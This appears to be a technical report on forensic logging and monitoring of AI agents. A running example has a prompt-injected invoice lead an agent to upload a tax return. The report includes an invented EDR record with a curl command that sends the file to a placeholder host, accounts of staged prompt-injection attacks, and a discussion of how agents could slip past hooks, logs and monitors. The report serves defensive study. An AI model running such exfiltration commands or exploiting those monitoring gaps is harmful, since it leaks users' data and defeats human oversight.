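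Reading a sensitive file is weak evidence of an attack, because coding agents routinely open files that contain passwords and connection settings. Elastic suggests comparing each machine with its own history. If a laptop normally shows four such reads a day, twenty in an hour from folders unrelated to the work are worth investigating.

Several things went wrong during the rollout. Cursor splits the script's path at spaces, so a script in a folder such as "Application Support" never ran and gave no error. Cursor also reads its hook settings only when it starts, so the deployment software reported success on every machine but no events arrived until Elastic began prompting people to restart the editor. The team also had to redesign the log format, because the first version put the same information in different places for different events, which made it hard to search.

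Other weaknesses are permanent. If the script crashes, Cursor by default carries on without logging the event, so a missing line doesn't prove that nothing happened. Cursor can instead block the action when a hook fails, but Elastic preferred not to block its engineers. A developer with administrator rights can remove the hooks, and on a Mac the user can edit the local log before it leaves the machine. An agent running under the user's account might be able to do the same. Elastic would notice if an active laptop stopped sending events, but a private owner probably has nobody watching for that.

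In the invoice case, Elastic's log would show the agent opening the seventeenth PDF and then running a command that named the tax return and an outside address. The central copy of the log would still be available on day 21. It would not contain the PDF's text, so an investigator could follow the sequence of actions but could not read the instructions that prompted them. Elastic acknowledges that a prompt-injected agent would be detectable only through its actions.

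### Keeping the context exactly as sent

To find out why the agent uploaded the tax return, an investigator needs the context the model had when it chose that step. A transcript may lack part of that context, as OpenClaw's did, and the missing part could contain the cause. The investigator also needs the original input to rerun the step without the suspicious PDF.

The simplest solution is to save each request as the agent program sends it. Claude Code's `OTEL_LOG_RAW_API_BODIES` switch exports the request and the response. When a user connects Claude Code to LangWatch, a tracing product, LangWatch automatically turns on this switch and the three switches for prompts and tool content.

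Even this copy omits anything the provider adds on its server, such as OpenAI's system message for Codex. Only the provider can supply that part. When tracing is on and Claude Code connects directly to Anthropic, it attaches the span's identifier to each model request, which could help Anthropic find its matching record.

Saving every request sounds expensive, because the agent program sends the whole context again for each model call. Suppose an agent makes 200 calls a day with an average context of 100,000 tokens, at about 4 bytes of text per token:

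200 × 100,000 × 4 bytes = 80,000,000 bytes, or 80 MB a day

That is 2.4 GB for 30 days, before compression. Most of each request repeats the previous one, so a program could store each piece of text once and keep, for every call, an ordered list of the pieces it contained. If 98% of each context repeats the one before, the program stores all 100,000 tokens for the first call and 2,000 for each of the other 199. The total is about 498,000 tokens, or 2 MB a day plus the lists. Images would add to this, but the text takes up little space on a modern laptop. The stronger objection is that such an archive collects everything private that the agent has read.

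### Aegis: refusing as well as recording

Elastic's script approves every action, but a program in the same position could refuse some. Nian and colleagues report tests of one such program, Aegis, which intercepts each tool call before it runs. Aegis extracts the text from the call's arguments, scans it for signs of risk and checks it against the operator's policies. It then allows the call, blocks it or holds it for a person to decide.

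Aegis added a median delay of 8.3 milliseconds over 1,000 consecutive calls, and 99% of the delays were no longer than 23.1 milliseconds. A user would not notice this, because a model typically takes between 1 and 30 seconds to respond. Aegis also blocked all 48 attacks in a curated set and wrongly flagged six of 500 harmless calls (1.2%).

The attack result is weak evidence of how Aegis would perform against a real attacker. The researchers selected the 48 attacks in advance, whereas an attacker can keep rewording an attack until one version gets through, as in the competition that Dziemian and colleagues ran. Even if the 48 had been a random sample of real attacks, a perfect score would be statistically compatible with a miss rate of up to about 6%. Many harmful calls also contain nothing suspicious. If the agent sends the tax return to a file-sharing service that the owner uses every week,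 the call's arguments look ordinary.

The harmless calls were also fairly simple, such as database queries and file reads. At the same error rate, an agent making 200 tool calls a day would trigger two or three false alarms. Owners who see that many may start approving requests without reading them.

The record that Aegis produces is its more valuable result for an investigator. It contains the tool's name, full arguments and output, the time and the decision, and Aegis signs it so that others can detect changes. Blocked, held and approved calls appear as separate events, so an auditor could tell a first attempt from a retry after a refusal. The record lacks the full chain of delegation behind a call.

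### Two draft formats

Every product discussed so far has its own log format, so an investigator has to learn each one. Two proposals for a common format have been submitted to the Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF), which develops many of the internet's technical standards. Both are individual Internet-Drafts, which people can submit without the IETF's endorsement, and each version expires after six months.

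In *An Architecture for Auditing Agent Delegation and Interactions*, Kühlewind and Birkholz (2026) propose that the user's software, the agent and the outside service each record their own side of an event, with a shared identifier to link the records, so that nobody has to trust an agent's account of itself. In their example, a traveller asks for a cheap flight and gets a business-class ticket that can't be cancelled. The traveller, a booking agency and an airline each had an agent involved, and without linked records the traveller can't tell which agent was at fault.

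The draft defines four types of record:

- *Interaction records* cover prompts, replies and approvals.
- *Action records* cover what happened at the point where an action took effect.
- *Delegation records* cover who gave authority to whom, and with what limits.
- *Authorization transition records* cover changes in what the agent was allowed to do.

An investigator could use the last type to work out which permissions the agent had during the upload. Under the draft, these records are kept in a store independent of the agent to make them stronger evidence.

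Kühlewind and Birkholz concede that their design does not help when a hostile service refuses to record what it did. This limit applies to the invoice case, because the attacker controls the site that received the tax return. The design is better suited to disputes between businesses that all have a reason to keep records. The field names are still placeholders, and the second version, dated 7 September 2026, expires on 11 March 2027.

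*Agent Audit Trail* (Sharif, 2026) proposes a more specific format. Each record must include the agent's identity and version, the session, the type of action and its outcome, and a fingerprint of the previous record. It must also state whether the program wrote it before, during or after the action. This last field is useful because a log entry written afterwards can show that an upload happened, but cannot prove that anyone checked the upload first. For a refusal to count as evidence, Sharif requires the program to record it before the action would have run.

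The format protects privacy by storing hashes, short fingerprints computed from the data, instead of the data. For the upload, the log would contain the tool's name and a hash of its arguments, but not the file or the address. An investigator could not recover the arguments from the log alone, but one who still had the transcript could recompute the hash and confirm that the arguments matched. Sharif allows raw data to be kept in a separate system, and a reconstruction would depend on someone having set that up.

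Leaving out the content saves less space than one might expect. Sharif's first version, from March 2026, estimates 10 to 20 MB a day for an agent that produces 10,000 records. The example above uses 2 MB to store 200 complete contexts without repetition, though its agent is much less busy.

Both versions of Sharif's draft give August 2026 as the start of the EU AI Act's requirement for automatic logs from high-risk AI systems. That date is outdated because the EU has postponed the duties for high-risk systems to 2 December 2027 and 2 August 2028, as The National Law Review reported in *EU Digital Omnibus on AI Enters Into Force* (July 2026). The amendment took effect on 27 July, more than three weeks before Sharif published the second version.

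### What a script can do unrecorded

The main limit of hooks and traces is that they record only what passes through the agent program. Suppose the hidden instructions in the seventeenth invoice tell the agent to write a script called `tidy.py` and run it. The script renames a few invoices, then opens the tax return and uploads it to an outside site. Elastic's log would show that the agent edited `tidy.py` and then ran `python tidy.py`. It would have no entry for the tax return or the outside site, because Python opened the file and made the connection without going through Cursor.

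A log that includes file contents would preserve the script's text, so an investigator could read what the script was meant to do. But a script can download more instructions when it runs, or behave differently depending on the date, so its text may not show everything it did. MCP servers raise the same problem. In the postmark-mcp case, a hook would have recorded only a normal request to send an email.

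Claude Code's tracing partly solves this problem. Claude Code passes the current span's identifier to each shell command it starts, so that a program can attach its own spans to the same tree. Anthropic intends this for scripts that cooperate by recording spans, which the author of a malicious script has no reason to include. To find out what `tidy.py` did, an investigator needs records from the operating system or the network.

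## What endpoint detection software sees

The script `tidy.py` could open the tax return and contact an outside site without going through the agent program, but it would still have to go through the operating system, where endpoint detection and response (EDR) software collects its records. Companies install EDR on staff computers to catch intruders. It records a new process in the same way whether a person, an agent or malware started it.

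### How EDR works

An EDR product consists of a sensor on each computer and a central service that stores the events and checks them for signs of attack. The sensor's sources depend on the operating system:

- On Windows, a driver asks the kernel, the core of the operating system, to notify it whenever a process starts or ends. Drivers can also follow file and network activity. PowerShell, a Windows command shell, passes scripts to the installed security software before running them, so the sensor may obtain their text. Python does not do this by default.
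- On macOS, Apple's Endpoint Security framework tells approved security programs when a process starts or opens a file. Separate network filters report connections.
- On Linux, sensors use the kernel's audit system or eBPF, a way of running small monitoring programs inside the kernel.

Windows includes the sensor for Microsoft Defender for Endpoint, but an organisation has to enrol each computer before the product works.

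When a process starts, the sensor usually records the time, the user account, the program's location and fingerprint, the full command line, and the parent process that started it. File events give the path and what the process did to the file. Network events give the remote address and port, and often the site's name. Most products record every new process but only some file reads, because a computer opens too many files to log them all. For `tidy.py`, EDR would probably show Python starting and connecting to an outside address, but might have no entry for the tax return.

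Each process has a parent, so the central service can arrange the events as a tree that shows which program started which. It also checks the events against alert rules, which describe suspicious patterns such as PowerShell decrypting a browser's saved passwords. A match can block the action, alert the security staff or add a note for later searches.

The sensor sends its events off the machine soon after they happen, and how long the service keeps them depends on the product and the contract. Microsoft's *Ignite 2026* (2026) announced 90 days of built-in retention for Defender data, in preview. The events of the invoice session would still be available on day 21, but they would be past the retention period if a leak were discovered after four months.

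### What a home computer records without EDR

Most private owners have antivirus software but no endpoint detection and response (EDR) software. Antivirus software looks for malware and does not keep a searchable history of every process. Windows can log each new process and record its command line, but both settings are off by default on home computers.

Some useful traces remain because Windows keeps them for other purposes. Prefetch, a feature that makes programs start faster, records the times of a program's last eight runs and some of the files it loaded at startup. Another component counts the bytes each program sends and receives, and usually keeps the totals for a month or more. On day 21, these records might show that the upload program ran on the afternoon of the invoice session and sent about two megabytes, but not where the data went.

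macOS writes a detailed system log but discards most of it within days or weeks, and the log has no routine entry for each command. Desktop versions of Linux typically log sign-ins and system services. People often look in the shell's history file first, but shells normally save only commands that someone typed at a prompt. An agent's commands usually run without a prompt and leave no line there.

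An owner can fill much of this gap in advance with free tools. Microsoft's Sysmon logs processes, connections and some file changes on Windows, and recent versions of macOS include the `eslogger` command, which prints events from the Endpoint Security framework. The records stay on the computer unless the owner copies them elsewhere.

### One upload in an EDR record

If the owner of the 40 invoices ran Codex on a Windows computer with EDR, and the agent uploaded the tax return with a single shell command, the record might look like the invented example below. Its process fields follow real records in *When the Whole Company Adopts AI* (Fishbein, 2026), published for the security company Intezer.

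```
Process started
  Time           14:32:07
  Account        owner
  Program        C:\Windows\System32\curl.exe
  Command line   curl.exe -F "file=@C:\Users\owner\Tax\return.pdf"
                 https://files.example/in
  Parent         powershell.exe
  Ancestors      codex.exe --yolo, started by node.exe

Network connection
  Program        curl.exe
  Remote         203.0.113.40, port 443
```

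This is strong evidence because it records the file, the destination and the time, and shows the command beneath Codex in the process tree. The `--yolo` option also lets Codex act without asking for approval, so the owner probably saw no prompt before the upload. Without that option, it would be unclear whether the owner saw a prompt, because a user can also relax approvals in the program's settings.

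The record does not establish whether the owner or the model chose the command. If an agent runs in its own window, its shell sits beneath a program such as `codex.exe` and has different ancestors from a shell the owner opened in a terminal. Elastic therefore overstates the problem for such agents when it argues, in its account of Cursor hooks, that EDR cannot distinguish an agent's commands from the developer's on the grounds that both run under the same account in processes the developer started. But some agent programs also let users type shell commands into them directly, and in a code editor such as Cursor, the owner's built-in terminal and the agent's shell can both descend from the editor. The process tree then looks much the same whoever chose the command.

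The record also doesn't show which document prompted the upload. If Codex used a separate program to extract the text from each PDF, the process tree would contain 40 such commands, and their timing would indicate which invoices the agent had read by 14:32, but the tree would not include the text of those invoices.

The software also doesn't record the contents of the connection, because `curl` encrypts the data before sending it. Here the command line happens to name the file, but if `tidy.py` had made the upload, an investigator would have only Python's connection to an unfamiliar address and perhaps a byte count to compare with the size of the tax return. The agent program's normal traffic to the model's provider is also encrypted. Fishbein calls the flow of company data to outside AI services "almost invisible to endpoint tooling".

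### Actions inside a browser or another running program

EDR records the most detail when a new process starts, and a browser agent may not need to start one. Suppose the owner's tax return is an attachment in webmail and the agent forwards it from there. The browser is already running and connected to the mail service, and the file is never written to disk. EDR would record, at most, more encrypted traffic between the browser and a service the owner uses all day, so an investigator would have to check the sent mail or ask the mail provider for its logs.

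When an agent program opens a file with a built-in tool instead of a shell command, it starts no new process, and the sensor may not record the read.

EDR records only part of what an MCP server does. It normally records the command that starts a local server, which would help a company find every machine that ran postmark-mcp. After that, the agent program and the server exchange messages without starting new processes. The postmark-mcp backdoor only altered emails that the server was already sending, so the computer made no extra connection for EDR to record.

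Some browser automation does start other programs. Sophos' *When AI agents look like attackers* (2026) describes GStack, a popular set of add-on skills that includes one for controlling a browser. When Claude Code used that skill, the process tree ran from a shell through the skill's own program to PowerShell, which decrypted protected browser data. Sophos considers this almost certainly harmless, but its software blocks the behaviour because password thieves do the same. EDR recorded how the agent gained access to the browser session, but not what it did on the websites.

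### How agents set off alerts

Many alert rules date from a time when few legitimate programs behaved like intruders. In one case from the Sophos data, Codex tried to download a Python installer from the official website using `certutil`, a Windows certificate tool that attackers often misuse to fetch files. Sophos blocked it. Codex tried again a second later with a different output path, made several more attempts ten minutes after that, and then switched to another tool that attackers favour, which Sophos also blocked. This kind of switch after a failure used to help analysts recognise a human intruder.

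Sophos examined seven days of Windows data from June 2026 and counted the machines on which agents triggered its rules. Rules about access to stored credentials made up 56.2% of the blocking matches, and rules about running suspicious code made up another 28.8%. Sophos describes the data as a first pass and gives no total number of machines, so the figures show which rules agents trigger but not how often.

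Fishbein's study is much larger. It covers about 16.9 million alerts from Intezer's corporate customers, of which about 73,000, or 0.43%, involved AI. Fishbein sorted these by the activity behind them:

| Class | Definition | Share of AI-related alerts |
|---|---|---|
| Real attack | A confirmed compromise or an attacker's operation | 0.02% |
| Risk | A genuine exposure without a compromise, such as an agent running with approvals turned off | 5.8% |
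| Noise | Legitimate activity that matched a rule written before agents existed | 94.1% |

The smallest class has about 15 alerts. According to Fishbein, none was a compromise caused by a company's own agent, and the confirmed attacks were phishing emails that used the names of AI companies as bait. Much of the noise came from routine activity. The genuine Claude Desktop installer set off a ransomware alert, and one rule at one customer, triggered by a coding agent setting up its working environment, produced 55% of all the alerts that Intezer's system rated critical.

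Fishbein reports that the number of AI-related alerts rose by 685% (almost eightfold) between February and June 2026, and gives the same figure for the rise in their share of all alerts. Both can be right only if the total number of alerts hardly changed. Another figure in the study is 18-fold growth in six months. It is safe to say that these alerts increased quickly among Intezer's customers, but not to assume a particular growth rate at other companies.

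Intezer also has a commercial interest in the result, since it sells software that investigates alerts automatically, and a large number of false alarms is a good reason to buy it. The company says the software passes fewer than 2% of alerts to a person (Mitchell, 2026, *Intezer launches custom AI agents for security teams*). In the study, Intezer's system closed 81.7% of the AI-related alerts without showing them to an analyst and escalated 5.4%.

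It is hard to know whether an alert is noise or a sign of silent compromise. Fishbein relies on inspection of each case but does not explain how the investigators ruled out prompt injection. In one example, Cursor used a known technique for dumping passwords from memory, and the study suggests that the agent was probably trying to fix a bug. The process tree supports the account of what Cursor did but cannot confirm why, and instructions in a poisoned file could equally have caused the same behavior. The study also counts only activity that raised an alert, so it would miss an upload that looked ordinary.

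CrowdStrike, another EDR vendor, describes the same figure in two different ways. CrowdStrike (2026) says in one summary of its annual threat report that agents now produce 2.5 times more leads for its analysts than manual activity does. Another summary says that leads from agents *grew* at 2.5 times the rate of those from people, which could be true even if agents still produced fewer. Expert Insights' *AI Agents Now Trigger Risky Endpoint Behavior* (2026) adopts the first reading and dates the figure to the first quarter of 2026.

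A lead is also very weak evidence. Security Management's *Artificial Intelligence Is the Weapon and the Target, CrowdStrike Report Finds* (2026) reports more than 14 million leads a day, from which CrowdStrike sends customers about 36,000 notifications a year, or roughly one for every 140,000 leads.

The proportions differ among cases that analysts have opened. In a separate review of a year's casework, Sophos examined 86 cases that staff had tagged as involving AI. It confirmed that attackers had used or exploited AI in 34 of them. Another 25 involved harmless developer tools, and the remaining 27 only contained an AI-related keyword.

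### Is conventional EDR blind to agents?

Chris Corde, chief product officer of SentinelOne, which sells EDR software, argued that agents' activities happen inside agent platforms and that "you can't actually see them with traditional EDRs" (Alspach, 2026, *SentinelOne’s Chris Corde On Why Traditional EDR Is ‘Flying Blind’*). The interview took place a week after SentinelOne launched a product for monitoring agents.

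A case that Elastic reconstructed from a developer's Mac puts this to the test. Elastic's EDR had been raising alerts on the machine since 20 July 2026, when it flagged software for private network connections. The next day, a general-purpose command touched Claude Code's memory file for a project. On 23 July, a Claude Code session with options for bypassing approvals did the following:

1. It repeatedly contacted a public web address until a login page answered, then sent a user name and password.
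2. It downloaded a summary of spending figures.
3. It opened a tunnel that made a service on the laptop reachable from the internet.
4. It installed background jobs to keep the tunnel running, including one that checked on it every 60 seconds.

EDR recorded much of this in detail, including the password on the command line. Elastic's analysts could connect the steps because the shells that ran them descended from Claude Code. But the sensor had not captured the options used to start the tunnel, so Elastic had to reconstruct a typical command. Later activity by a second tunnel program appeared under the Mac's service manager instead of the agent, because background jobs do not descend from the session that installed them.

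The analysts could not determine whether this was an attack. The owner might have asked Claude Code to make a private dashboard available while they were travelling, but an intruder who wanted lasting access to the dashboard would have needed almost the same commands. Elastic leaves both explanations open and advises analysts to write down what the evidence can and cannot support. Process events don't include the owner's request or the text the agent had read, which might have settled the question.

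Corde's claim is therefore wrong about shell commands and the programs they start, but largely right about prompts, the documents that led to an action, and work inside a browser. SentinelOne addresses this gap by combining its EDR sensor with software that captures the prompt, so that an analyst can trace a request to its effects.

Corde also describes Claude on a laptop as a virtual machine (a simulated computer with its own operating system) with the model embedded in it, but the model runs on Anthropic's servers. When an agent program does run its commands in a virtual machine, a sensor on the laptop normally records the virtual machine as one process and cannot list the commands inside. Fishbein advises running agents in a virtual machine or a container, a lighter form of isolation, to keep their activity separate from the user's. This limits the damage an agent can do and makes it clearer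 who acted, but a company may need a second sensor inside to record the individual commands.

### What Defender and other products now add

EDR vendors have responded with two kinds of feature. *Discovery* lists the agents on each computer, and *runtime protection* examines what an agent reads and does. Microsoft offers both in Defender for Endpoint.

According to Microsoft's *Now generally available* (2026), Defender can discover more than 50 agents and MCP servers on Windows and macOS. For each agent, it lists the version, device, user account and any MCP servers found in the agent's configuration. Microsoft also documents fields for the date Defender first saw the agent and whether the agent approves its own actions. These records could show an investigator that an agent was on the machine before the leak and had a suspicious MCP server configured. The inventory does not separate sessions.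 It has one entry for each combination of user, device and agent type, so Claude Code running in 15 project folders appears only once.

Defender's runtime protection works mainly through hooks. It checks for prompt injection in the user's prompt, each tool call before it runs, and each tool result. In audit mode it raises an alert but lets the action continue, while in block mode it stops the action. For agents without suitable hooks, Defender can inspect the traffic between the agent and the model. Jeffrey Appel, who writes guides to Microsoft security products, notes that this inspection does not work for agents that accept only a specific security certificate or that use HTTP/3, a newer web protocol.

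| Defender feature | Status | Agents covered |
|---|---|---|
| Discovery | Generally available on Windows and macOS | More than 50 agents and MCP servers, including Claude Code, Codex, Cursor, ChatGPT Desktop and OpenClaw |
| Runtime protection through hooks | Preview on Windows | Claude Code, GitHub Copilot's command-line and desktop apps, Claude Desktop in Code mode, and VS Code extensions for Claude Code and Copilot |
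| Runtime protection through network inspection | Preview on Windows | OpenClaw, Ollama Desktop, ChatGPT Classic, and ChatGPT Desktop in Chat mode |

The runtime lists come from Appel. *Security Monitoring of AI Agents in Microsoft Defender XDR* (Scalzi, 2026), written for the firm Compass Security, also lists Codex's command-line program, which Appel omits. A company that relies on Codex should test whether protection works on its own machines. Scalzi and Appel both say runtime protection requires the beta version of Defender, and both advise against installing the beta widely yet.

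The licence terms are confusing. Microsoft says discovery and runtime protection require Defender for Endpoint Plan 2 or higher. For runtime protection, Appel also lists Microsoft 365 E5, Microsoft 365 E7 and Agent 365, Microsoft's service for managing agents. Scalzi warns that companies may need Agent 365 or E7, but the warning covers both cloud and local agents. Licensing School's *Agent 365 FAQs* (2026) says E5 does not include Agent 365, but discovery of AI on computers comes with a Microsoft cloud subscription. A company with E5 can therefore probably use the local features without buying Agent 365. These are all business licences, which the private owner of the 40 invoices is unlikely to have.

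Other vendors sell similar features. Sysdig (2026) launched detection rules for Claude Code, Codex and Gemini in March, and Elastic has rules for programs that agents start and background jobs they install.

If the owner's computer had runtime protection that supported the agent, Defender could have scanned the seventeenth invoice when the tool returned its text. Microsoft says an alert includes the affected agent and its process tree, so a detection would have pointed to the right session on the day of the leak instead of three weeks later. In audit mode, however, Defender marks such alerts as informational and would have let the upload go ahead. Microsoft describes the scans as brief checks at set points, not continuous monitoring of the agent. If Defender had failed to recognise the hidden instructions, it would have raised no prompt-injection alert, and the investigator would have had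 to work from the process and network events.

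## Linking instructions to their effects on the machine

To connect the hidden instructions in a transcript to an EDR record of the upload, an investigator must show that the instructions led to a particular tool call, and that this call started the process that sent the tax return. Researchers have used *provenance graphs* to trace chains of processes and files for more than twenty years. Each node in the graph is a process, file, message or tool call, and each edge shows that one node influenced another.

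### Tracing backward from a harmful effect

*Backtracking Intrusions* (King and Chen, 2003) describes BackTracker, a program that helps find out how an intruder got into a Linux computer. It logs events through which one object can affect another, such as a process starting a second process or reading a file. An administrator later gives it a suspicious file or process, and BackTracker works backward through the log to find everything that could have affected it.

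Suppose the agent used the script `tidy.py` for the upload, and the log contains these events:

```
1  Agent program reads invoice 16
2  Agent program reads invoice 17
3  Agent program writes tidy.py
4  Agent program starts Python
5  Python reads tidy.py
6  Python reads return.pdf
7  Python sends data to the outside site
8  Agent program reads invoice 18
```

The search starts with the data that reached the outside site and reads the log backward. Event 8 affects only the agent program, which is not in the graph yet, so BackTracker skips it. Event 7 adds Python. Events 6 and 5 add the tax return and the script, because Python read both before it sent anything. Event 4 adds the agent program, event 3 links it to the script, and events 2 and 1 add the two invoices.

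BackTracker adds each object to the graph with a time limit and ignores anything that happened to the object after that time. If the agent overwrote `tidy.py` after the upload to hide what it had done, the later write would not appear as a cause. *SPARSE* (2024) states the rule formally. If u₁ affected v₁ at time t₁ and u₂ affected v₂ at time t₂, the second event depends on the first when v₁ = u₂ and t₁ < t₂. *vCause* (2026) describes a refinement that creates a new node whenever a file or process changes, which keeps the script that ran separate from the version that replaced it.

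King and Chen tried BackTracker on computers they had set up to attract attackers. In one attack from March 2003, they noticed an unfamiliar process, and the graph traced it back through a command shell to the web server where the intruder had entered. The logging slowed a demanding workload by 9% and produced 1.2 GB a day. At that rate, three weeks of logs would take up about 25 GB, which most modern laptops could hold.

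### Too many possible causes

Invoice 16 was harmless but is still in the graph. The operating system can record that the agent program read the invoice before writing the script, but not whether the invoice affected the script. *ProTracer* (2016) describes the usual cautious assumption that every input influences all later outputs. If a long-running program reads 50 files and then writes 20, this gives 50 × 20 = 1,000 candidate links, most of them probably false. Researchers call this problem *dependency explosion*.

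On a real machine the graph is much larger. *A Benign Activity Extraction Method for Malignant Activity Identification using Data Provenance* (2025) notes that a graph can have over a million edges, while technical managers who handle EDR products want to see about 10 to 100. For one data leak, *SPARSE* used filtering to reduce a backward graph from about 200,000 edges to about 22.

Another remedy is to divide a program's run into units, such as the handling of one email, and link an output only to earlier inputs in the same unit. *Accurate, Low Cost and Instrumentation-Free* describes a way to do this from Windows' own event records without altering the programs. For an agent program, tool calls are convenient units. Suppose 20 tool calls write one file each, and the 50 reads are divided among them. Each read then pairs with only one write, so 50 candidate links remain instead of 1,000.

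But this also removes the link that matters most in the invoice case. The agent read invoice 17 in one tool call and uploaded the tax return in another. The influence passed through the model's context, which also contained the text of all the earlier invoices. *HANSARD* (Sardianos, Pla and colleagues, 2026), a proposed design for forensic records of AI agents, argues that dependency explosion is worse inside a shared context than in ordinary software, because every piece of text in it could have influenced every later action. It also points out that influence through language leaves no edge that the operating system can observe.

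The content of the calls can reveal some of these links. *AgentTrails* (2026) adds an edge when a later tool call explicitly refers to something an earlier call produced. If the upload address appears in the text of invoice 17 and nowhere else in the context, that invoice is the most likely source. The method is less useful for the path of the tax return, which the agent may have found by listing a folder.

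### How AgentSight joins model traffic to system events

Zheng, Yu and colleagues (2025), in *AgentSight*, combine the model's messages with the operating system's events. Their tool works outside the agent program, so it does not depend on the program's own logs:

1. AgentSight attaches small monitoring programs to the encryption library that the agent program uses. These copy requests before encryption and responses after decryption.
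2. Other monitoring programs in the Linux kernel report when a process starts, opens a file or makes a connection. A filter keeps only the events of the agent program and its descendants.
3. AgentSight joins the messages to the events using process ancestry, timing and matching arguments. For timing, it looks for actions within a window of 100 to 500 milliseconds after a model response. For arguments, it looks for file names, addresses or commands from the response that reappear in a system event.
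4. A second language model reads the joined trace, judges whether it looks like an attack and explains why.

Suppose the model requests a `curl` command that uploads `return.pdf`, and 200 milliseconds later a descendant of the agent program starts `curl` with the same file and address. The process's ancestry, arguments and timing all suggest that it came from the model's request.

Zheng and colleagues tested AgentSight on a staged prompt injection. They asked an agent to download and build a software project whose README file pointed to a web page with hidden instructions. The agent followed them and used a command disguised as a build step to send the computer's list of user accounts to an outside server. AgentSight captured the chain from the web page to the upload and merged 521 events into 37, few enough for a person to read. The second model flagged the actions as inconsistent with the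 agent's task.

This shows that the method can work, but the evidence comes from a single attack. Zheng and colleagues do not report how often AgentSight makes a wrong link or flags harmless work. The second model reads the attacker's text, so the attacker could try to mislead it too.

They measured the slowdown with Claude Code on three tasks, running each three times with AgentSight and three times without:

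| Task | Without AgentSight | With AgentSight | Overhead |
|---|---|---|---|
| Understanding a code repository | 127.98 s | 132.33 s | 3.4% |
| Writing code | 22.54 s | 23.64 s | 4.9% |
| Compiling a repository | 92.40 s | 92.72 s | 0.4% |

The paper's claim of less than 3% is based on the average slowdown of 2.9%, but two of the three tasks exceeded 3%. Three runs are too few to measure small differences well, because a model's response time can vary by a second or more. Still, a user probably wouldn't notice a slowdown of this size.

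AgentSight needs administrator rights, and it has to find the encryption library that the agent uses. Claude Code and some other agent programs contain their own copy of the library instead of using the system's, according to the project's documentation, eunomia-bpf's *agentsight 0.2.25*. AgentSight finds that copy automatically when it starts the agent, but the user may have to specify its location if the agent is already running. The documentation for a later release, eunomia-bpf's *agentsight 1.0.29*, lists Codex, OpenCode and OpenClaw among the programs AgentSight can observe.

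### What timing and matching can get wrong

Zheng and colleagues write that their three signals "definitively establish" causal relationships, but that claim is too strong. If the owner takes ten seconds to approve a command, the command starts after the 500-millisecond window has closed. A background task the agent started earlier may open a file just after an unrelated response and be wrongly linked to it. Matching arguments fails if `tidy.py` assembles the upload address from fragments, and it can produce false links when many actions involve the same common file name. Process ancestry is more reliable, but it shows only that the action came from a process descended from the agent program, not which response prompted it.

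Wong and Chen (2026), in *ExecWeave*, treat the same kind of link as an inference. Their tool takes a command that the agent requested and looks for processes that match it, by default within three seconds. Let s be the requested command and K(s) the set of matching processes that the tool observed. Its answer φ(s) is:

φ(s) = r, if K(s) contains only the process r
φ(s) = ⊥ (no answer), otherwise

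If two agents on the same computer both run `python tidy.py` within a second of each other, ExecWeave finds two candidates and makes no link. A tool that always picked the process nearest in time would sometimes attribute it to the wrong agent. ExecWeave labels each link it does make as inferred and non-causal, and keeps the supporting events so that an investigator can check them.

Despite this caution, ExecWeave links to the wrong process if the collector misses the true one and records one similar process, because that leaves a single candidate. Wong and Chen produced this error deliberately in a test and call it "false uniqueness". They also found that a much simpler rule, which uses only the program's path, did as well as their full matching method on the test cases.

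ExecWeave's portable collector can miss processes because it takes snapshots at intervals instead of receiving every event. In tests with processes that lasted about 16 milliseconds, it detected 18 of 30 with a snapshot every 20 milliseconds and none of 30 with one every 500 milliseconds. At the slower rate, it also missed more than half of the processes that lasted about a quarter of a second.

The collector also slowed three test workloads, increasing their running times by 408.8%, 85.2% and 62.3%. The largest increase was on a task that normally takes less than a tenth of a second. These figures are not directly comparable with AgentSight's, because the workloads did little except handle files and start processes, while AgentSight's test tasks included waiting for a model.

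A shared identifier would remove much of the guesswork. With tracing on, Claude Code already passes one to the shell commands it starts, but a malicious script need not pass it on.

### Agent-Warden and files that carry influence

AgentSight's filter discards events from programs that do not descend from the agent. An attacker could exploit this by having the agent leave a file for another program to act on. Cui, Gu and colleagues (2026), in *Agent-Warden*, address this gap with a Linux tool that marks the agent's process and passes the mark on through four rules:

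| Event | What receives the mark |
|---|---|
| A marked process starts another process | The new process |
| A marked process writes to a file | The file |
| A process reads a marked file | The process that read it |
| A marked process ends | Its parent process |

Each mark is either 0 or 1. When an event carries influence from a source to a target, the tool updates the target's mark:

new mark of target = old mark of target OR mark of source

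A process or file therefore stays marked even if its later activity has nothing to do with the agent.

Suppose the owner has a backup program that runs every night and uploads the files named in `backup-list.txt`. The instructions in invoice 17 tell the agent to add the tax return to the list and to change the backup's destination, which the list also contains. The marks then spread as follows:

1. The agent starts a shell, which inherits the mark.
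2. The shell writes the new list to a temporary file, which becomes marked, and renames it `backup-list.txt`. The mark stays, because Agent-Warden attaches it to the file itself and not to its name.
3. At 23:00 the system's scheduler starts the backup program, which has no mark because the agent did not start it.
4. The backup program reads the list and becomes marked.

The graph now connects the backup program to the agent, even though the agent had finished hours earlier. Agent-Warden does not yet follow network connections, so the investigator would need EDR or network records to show the upload itself.

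When the backup program ends, the fourth rule marks the scheduler. Under the first rule, every program that the scheduler starts from then on inherits the mark, even if it never touched anything from the agent. Cui and colleagues accept such false links on purpose, so that an agent cannot break the chain by working through a helper process that exits almost immediately. On a busy machine, however, marks could spread so widely that they are of little use in identifying what the agent influenced. An investigator can use them to decide where to look for further damage, but a mark alone does not show that any data passed between two programs.

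In an experiment by Cui and colleagues, an agent started a script that wrote a temporary file and renamed it. A monitoring script, which the agent had not started, later read the file. Langfuse, a tool that traces what happens inside an agent program, recorded nothing after the agent's involvement with the file ended, while Agent-Warden reconstructed the whole sequence of events. The team ran the test 30 times with each of two versions of Agent-Warden on each of two computers, and all 120 runs gave the expected result.

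The researchers designed the scenario around their own rules and checked only that the expected links appeared. They did not count false links, the number an investigator would most want to know for a tool designed to over-link.

Agent-Warden had low overhead. In a stress test that repeatedly started processes and handled files, one version added 0.2% to the running time on a desktop processor and another added 1.1%. On a slower ARM processor, the increase was 3.5%. The 0.2% figure had a standard deviation of 1.2 percentage points, so it is indistinguishable from no slowdown.

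Agent-Warden also misses some activity, such as a program accessing a file by mapping it into memory. It keeps its marks in working memory, so they disappear when the machine restarts. If the owner had shut the laptop down before 23:00 and the backup had run the next morning, the backup program would have read an unmarked list.

### Where each argument came from

Neither AgentSight nor Agent-Warden records which part of the context supplied the upload address. *Agent-Sentry* (Sequeira et al., 2026) collects this information inside the agent. It adds instructions to the agent's prompt and extra fields to its tools, so that the model must give a source for every argument of every call and state whether it copied the value word for word, derived it from the source or generated it. Agent-Sentry removes the extra fields before the tool runs.

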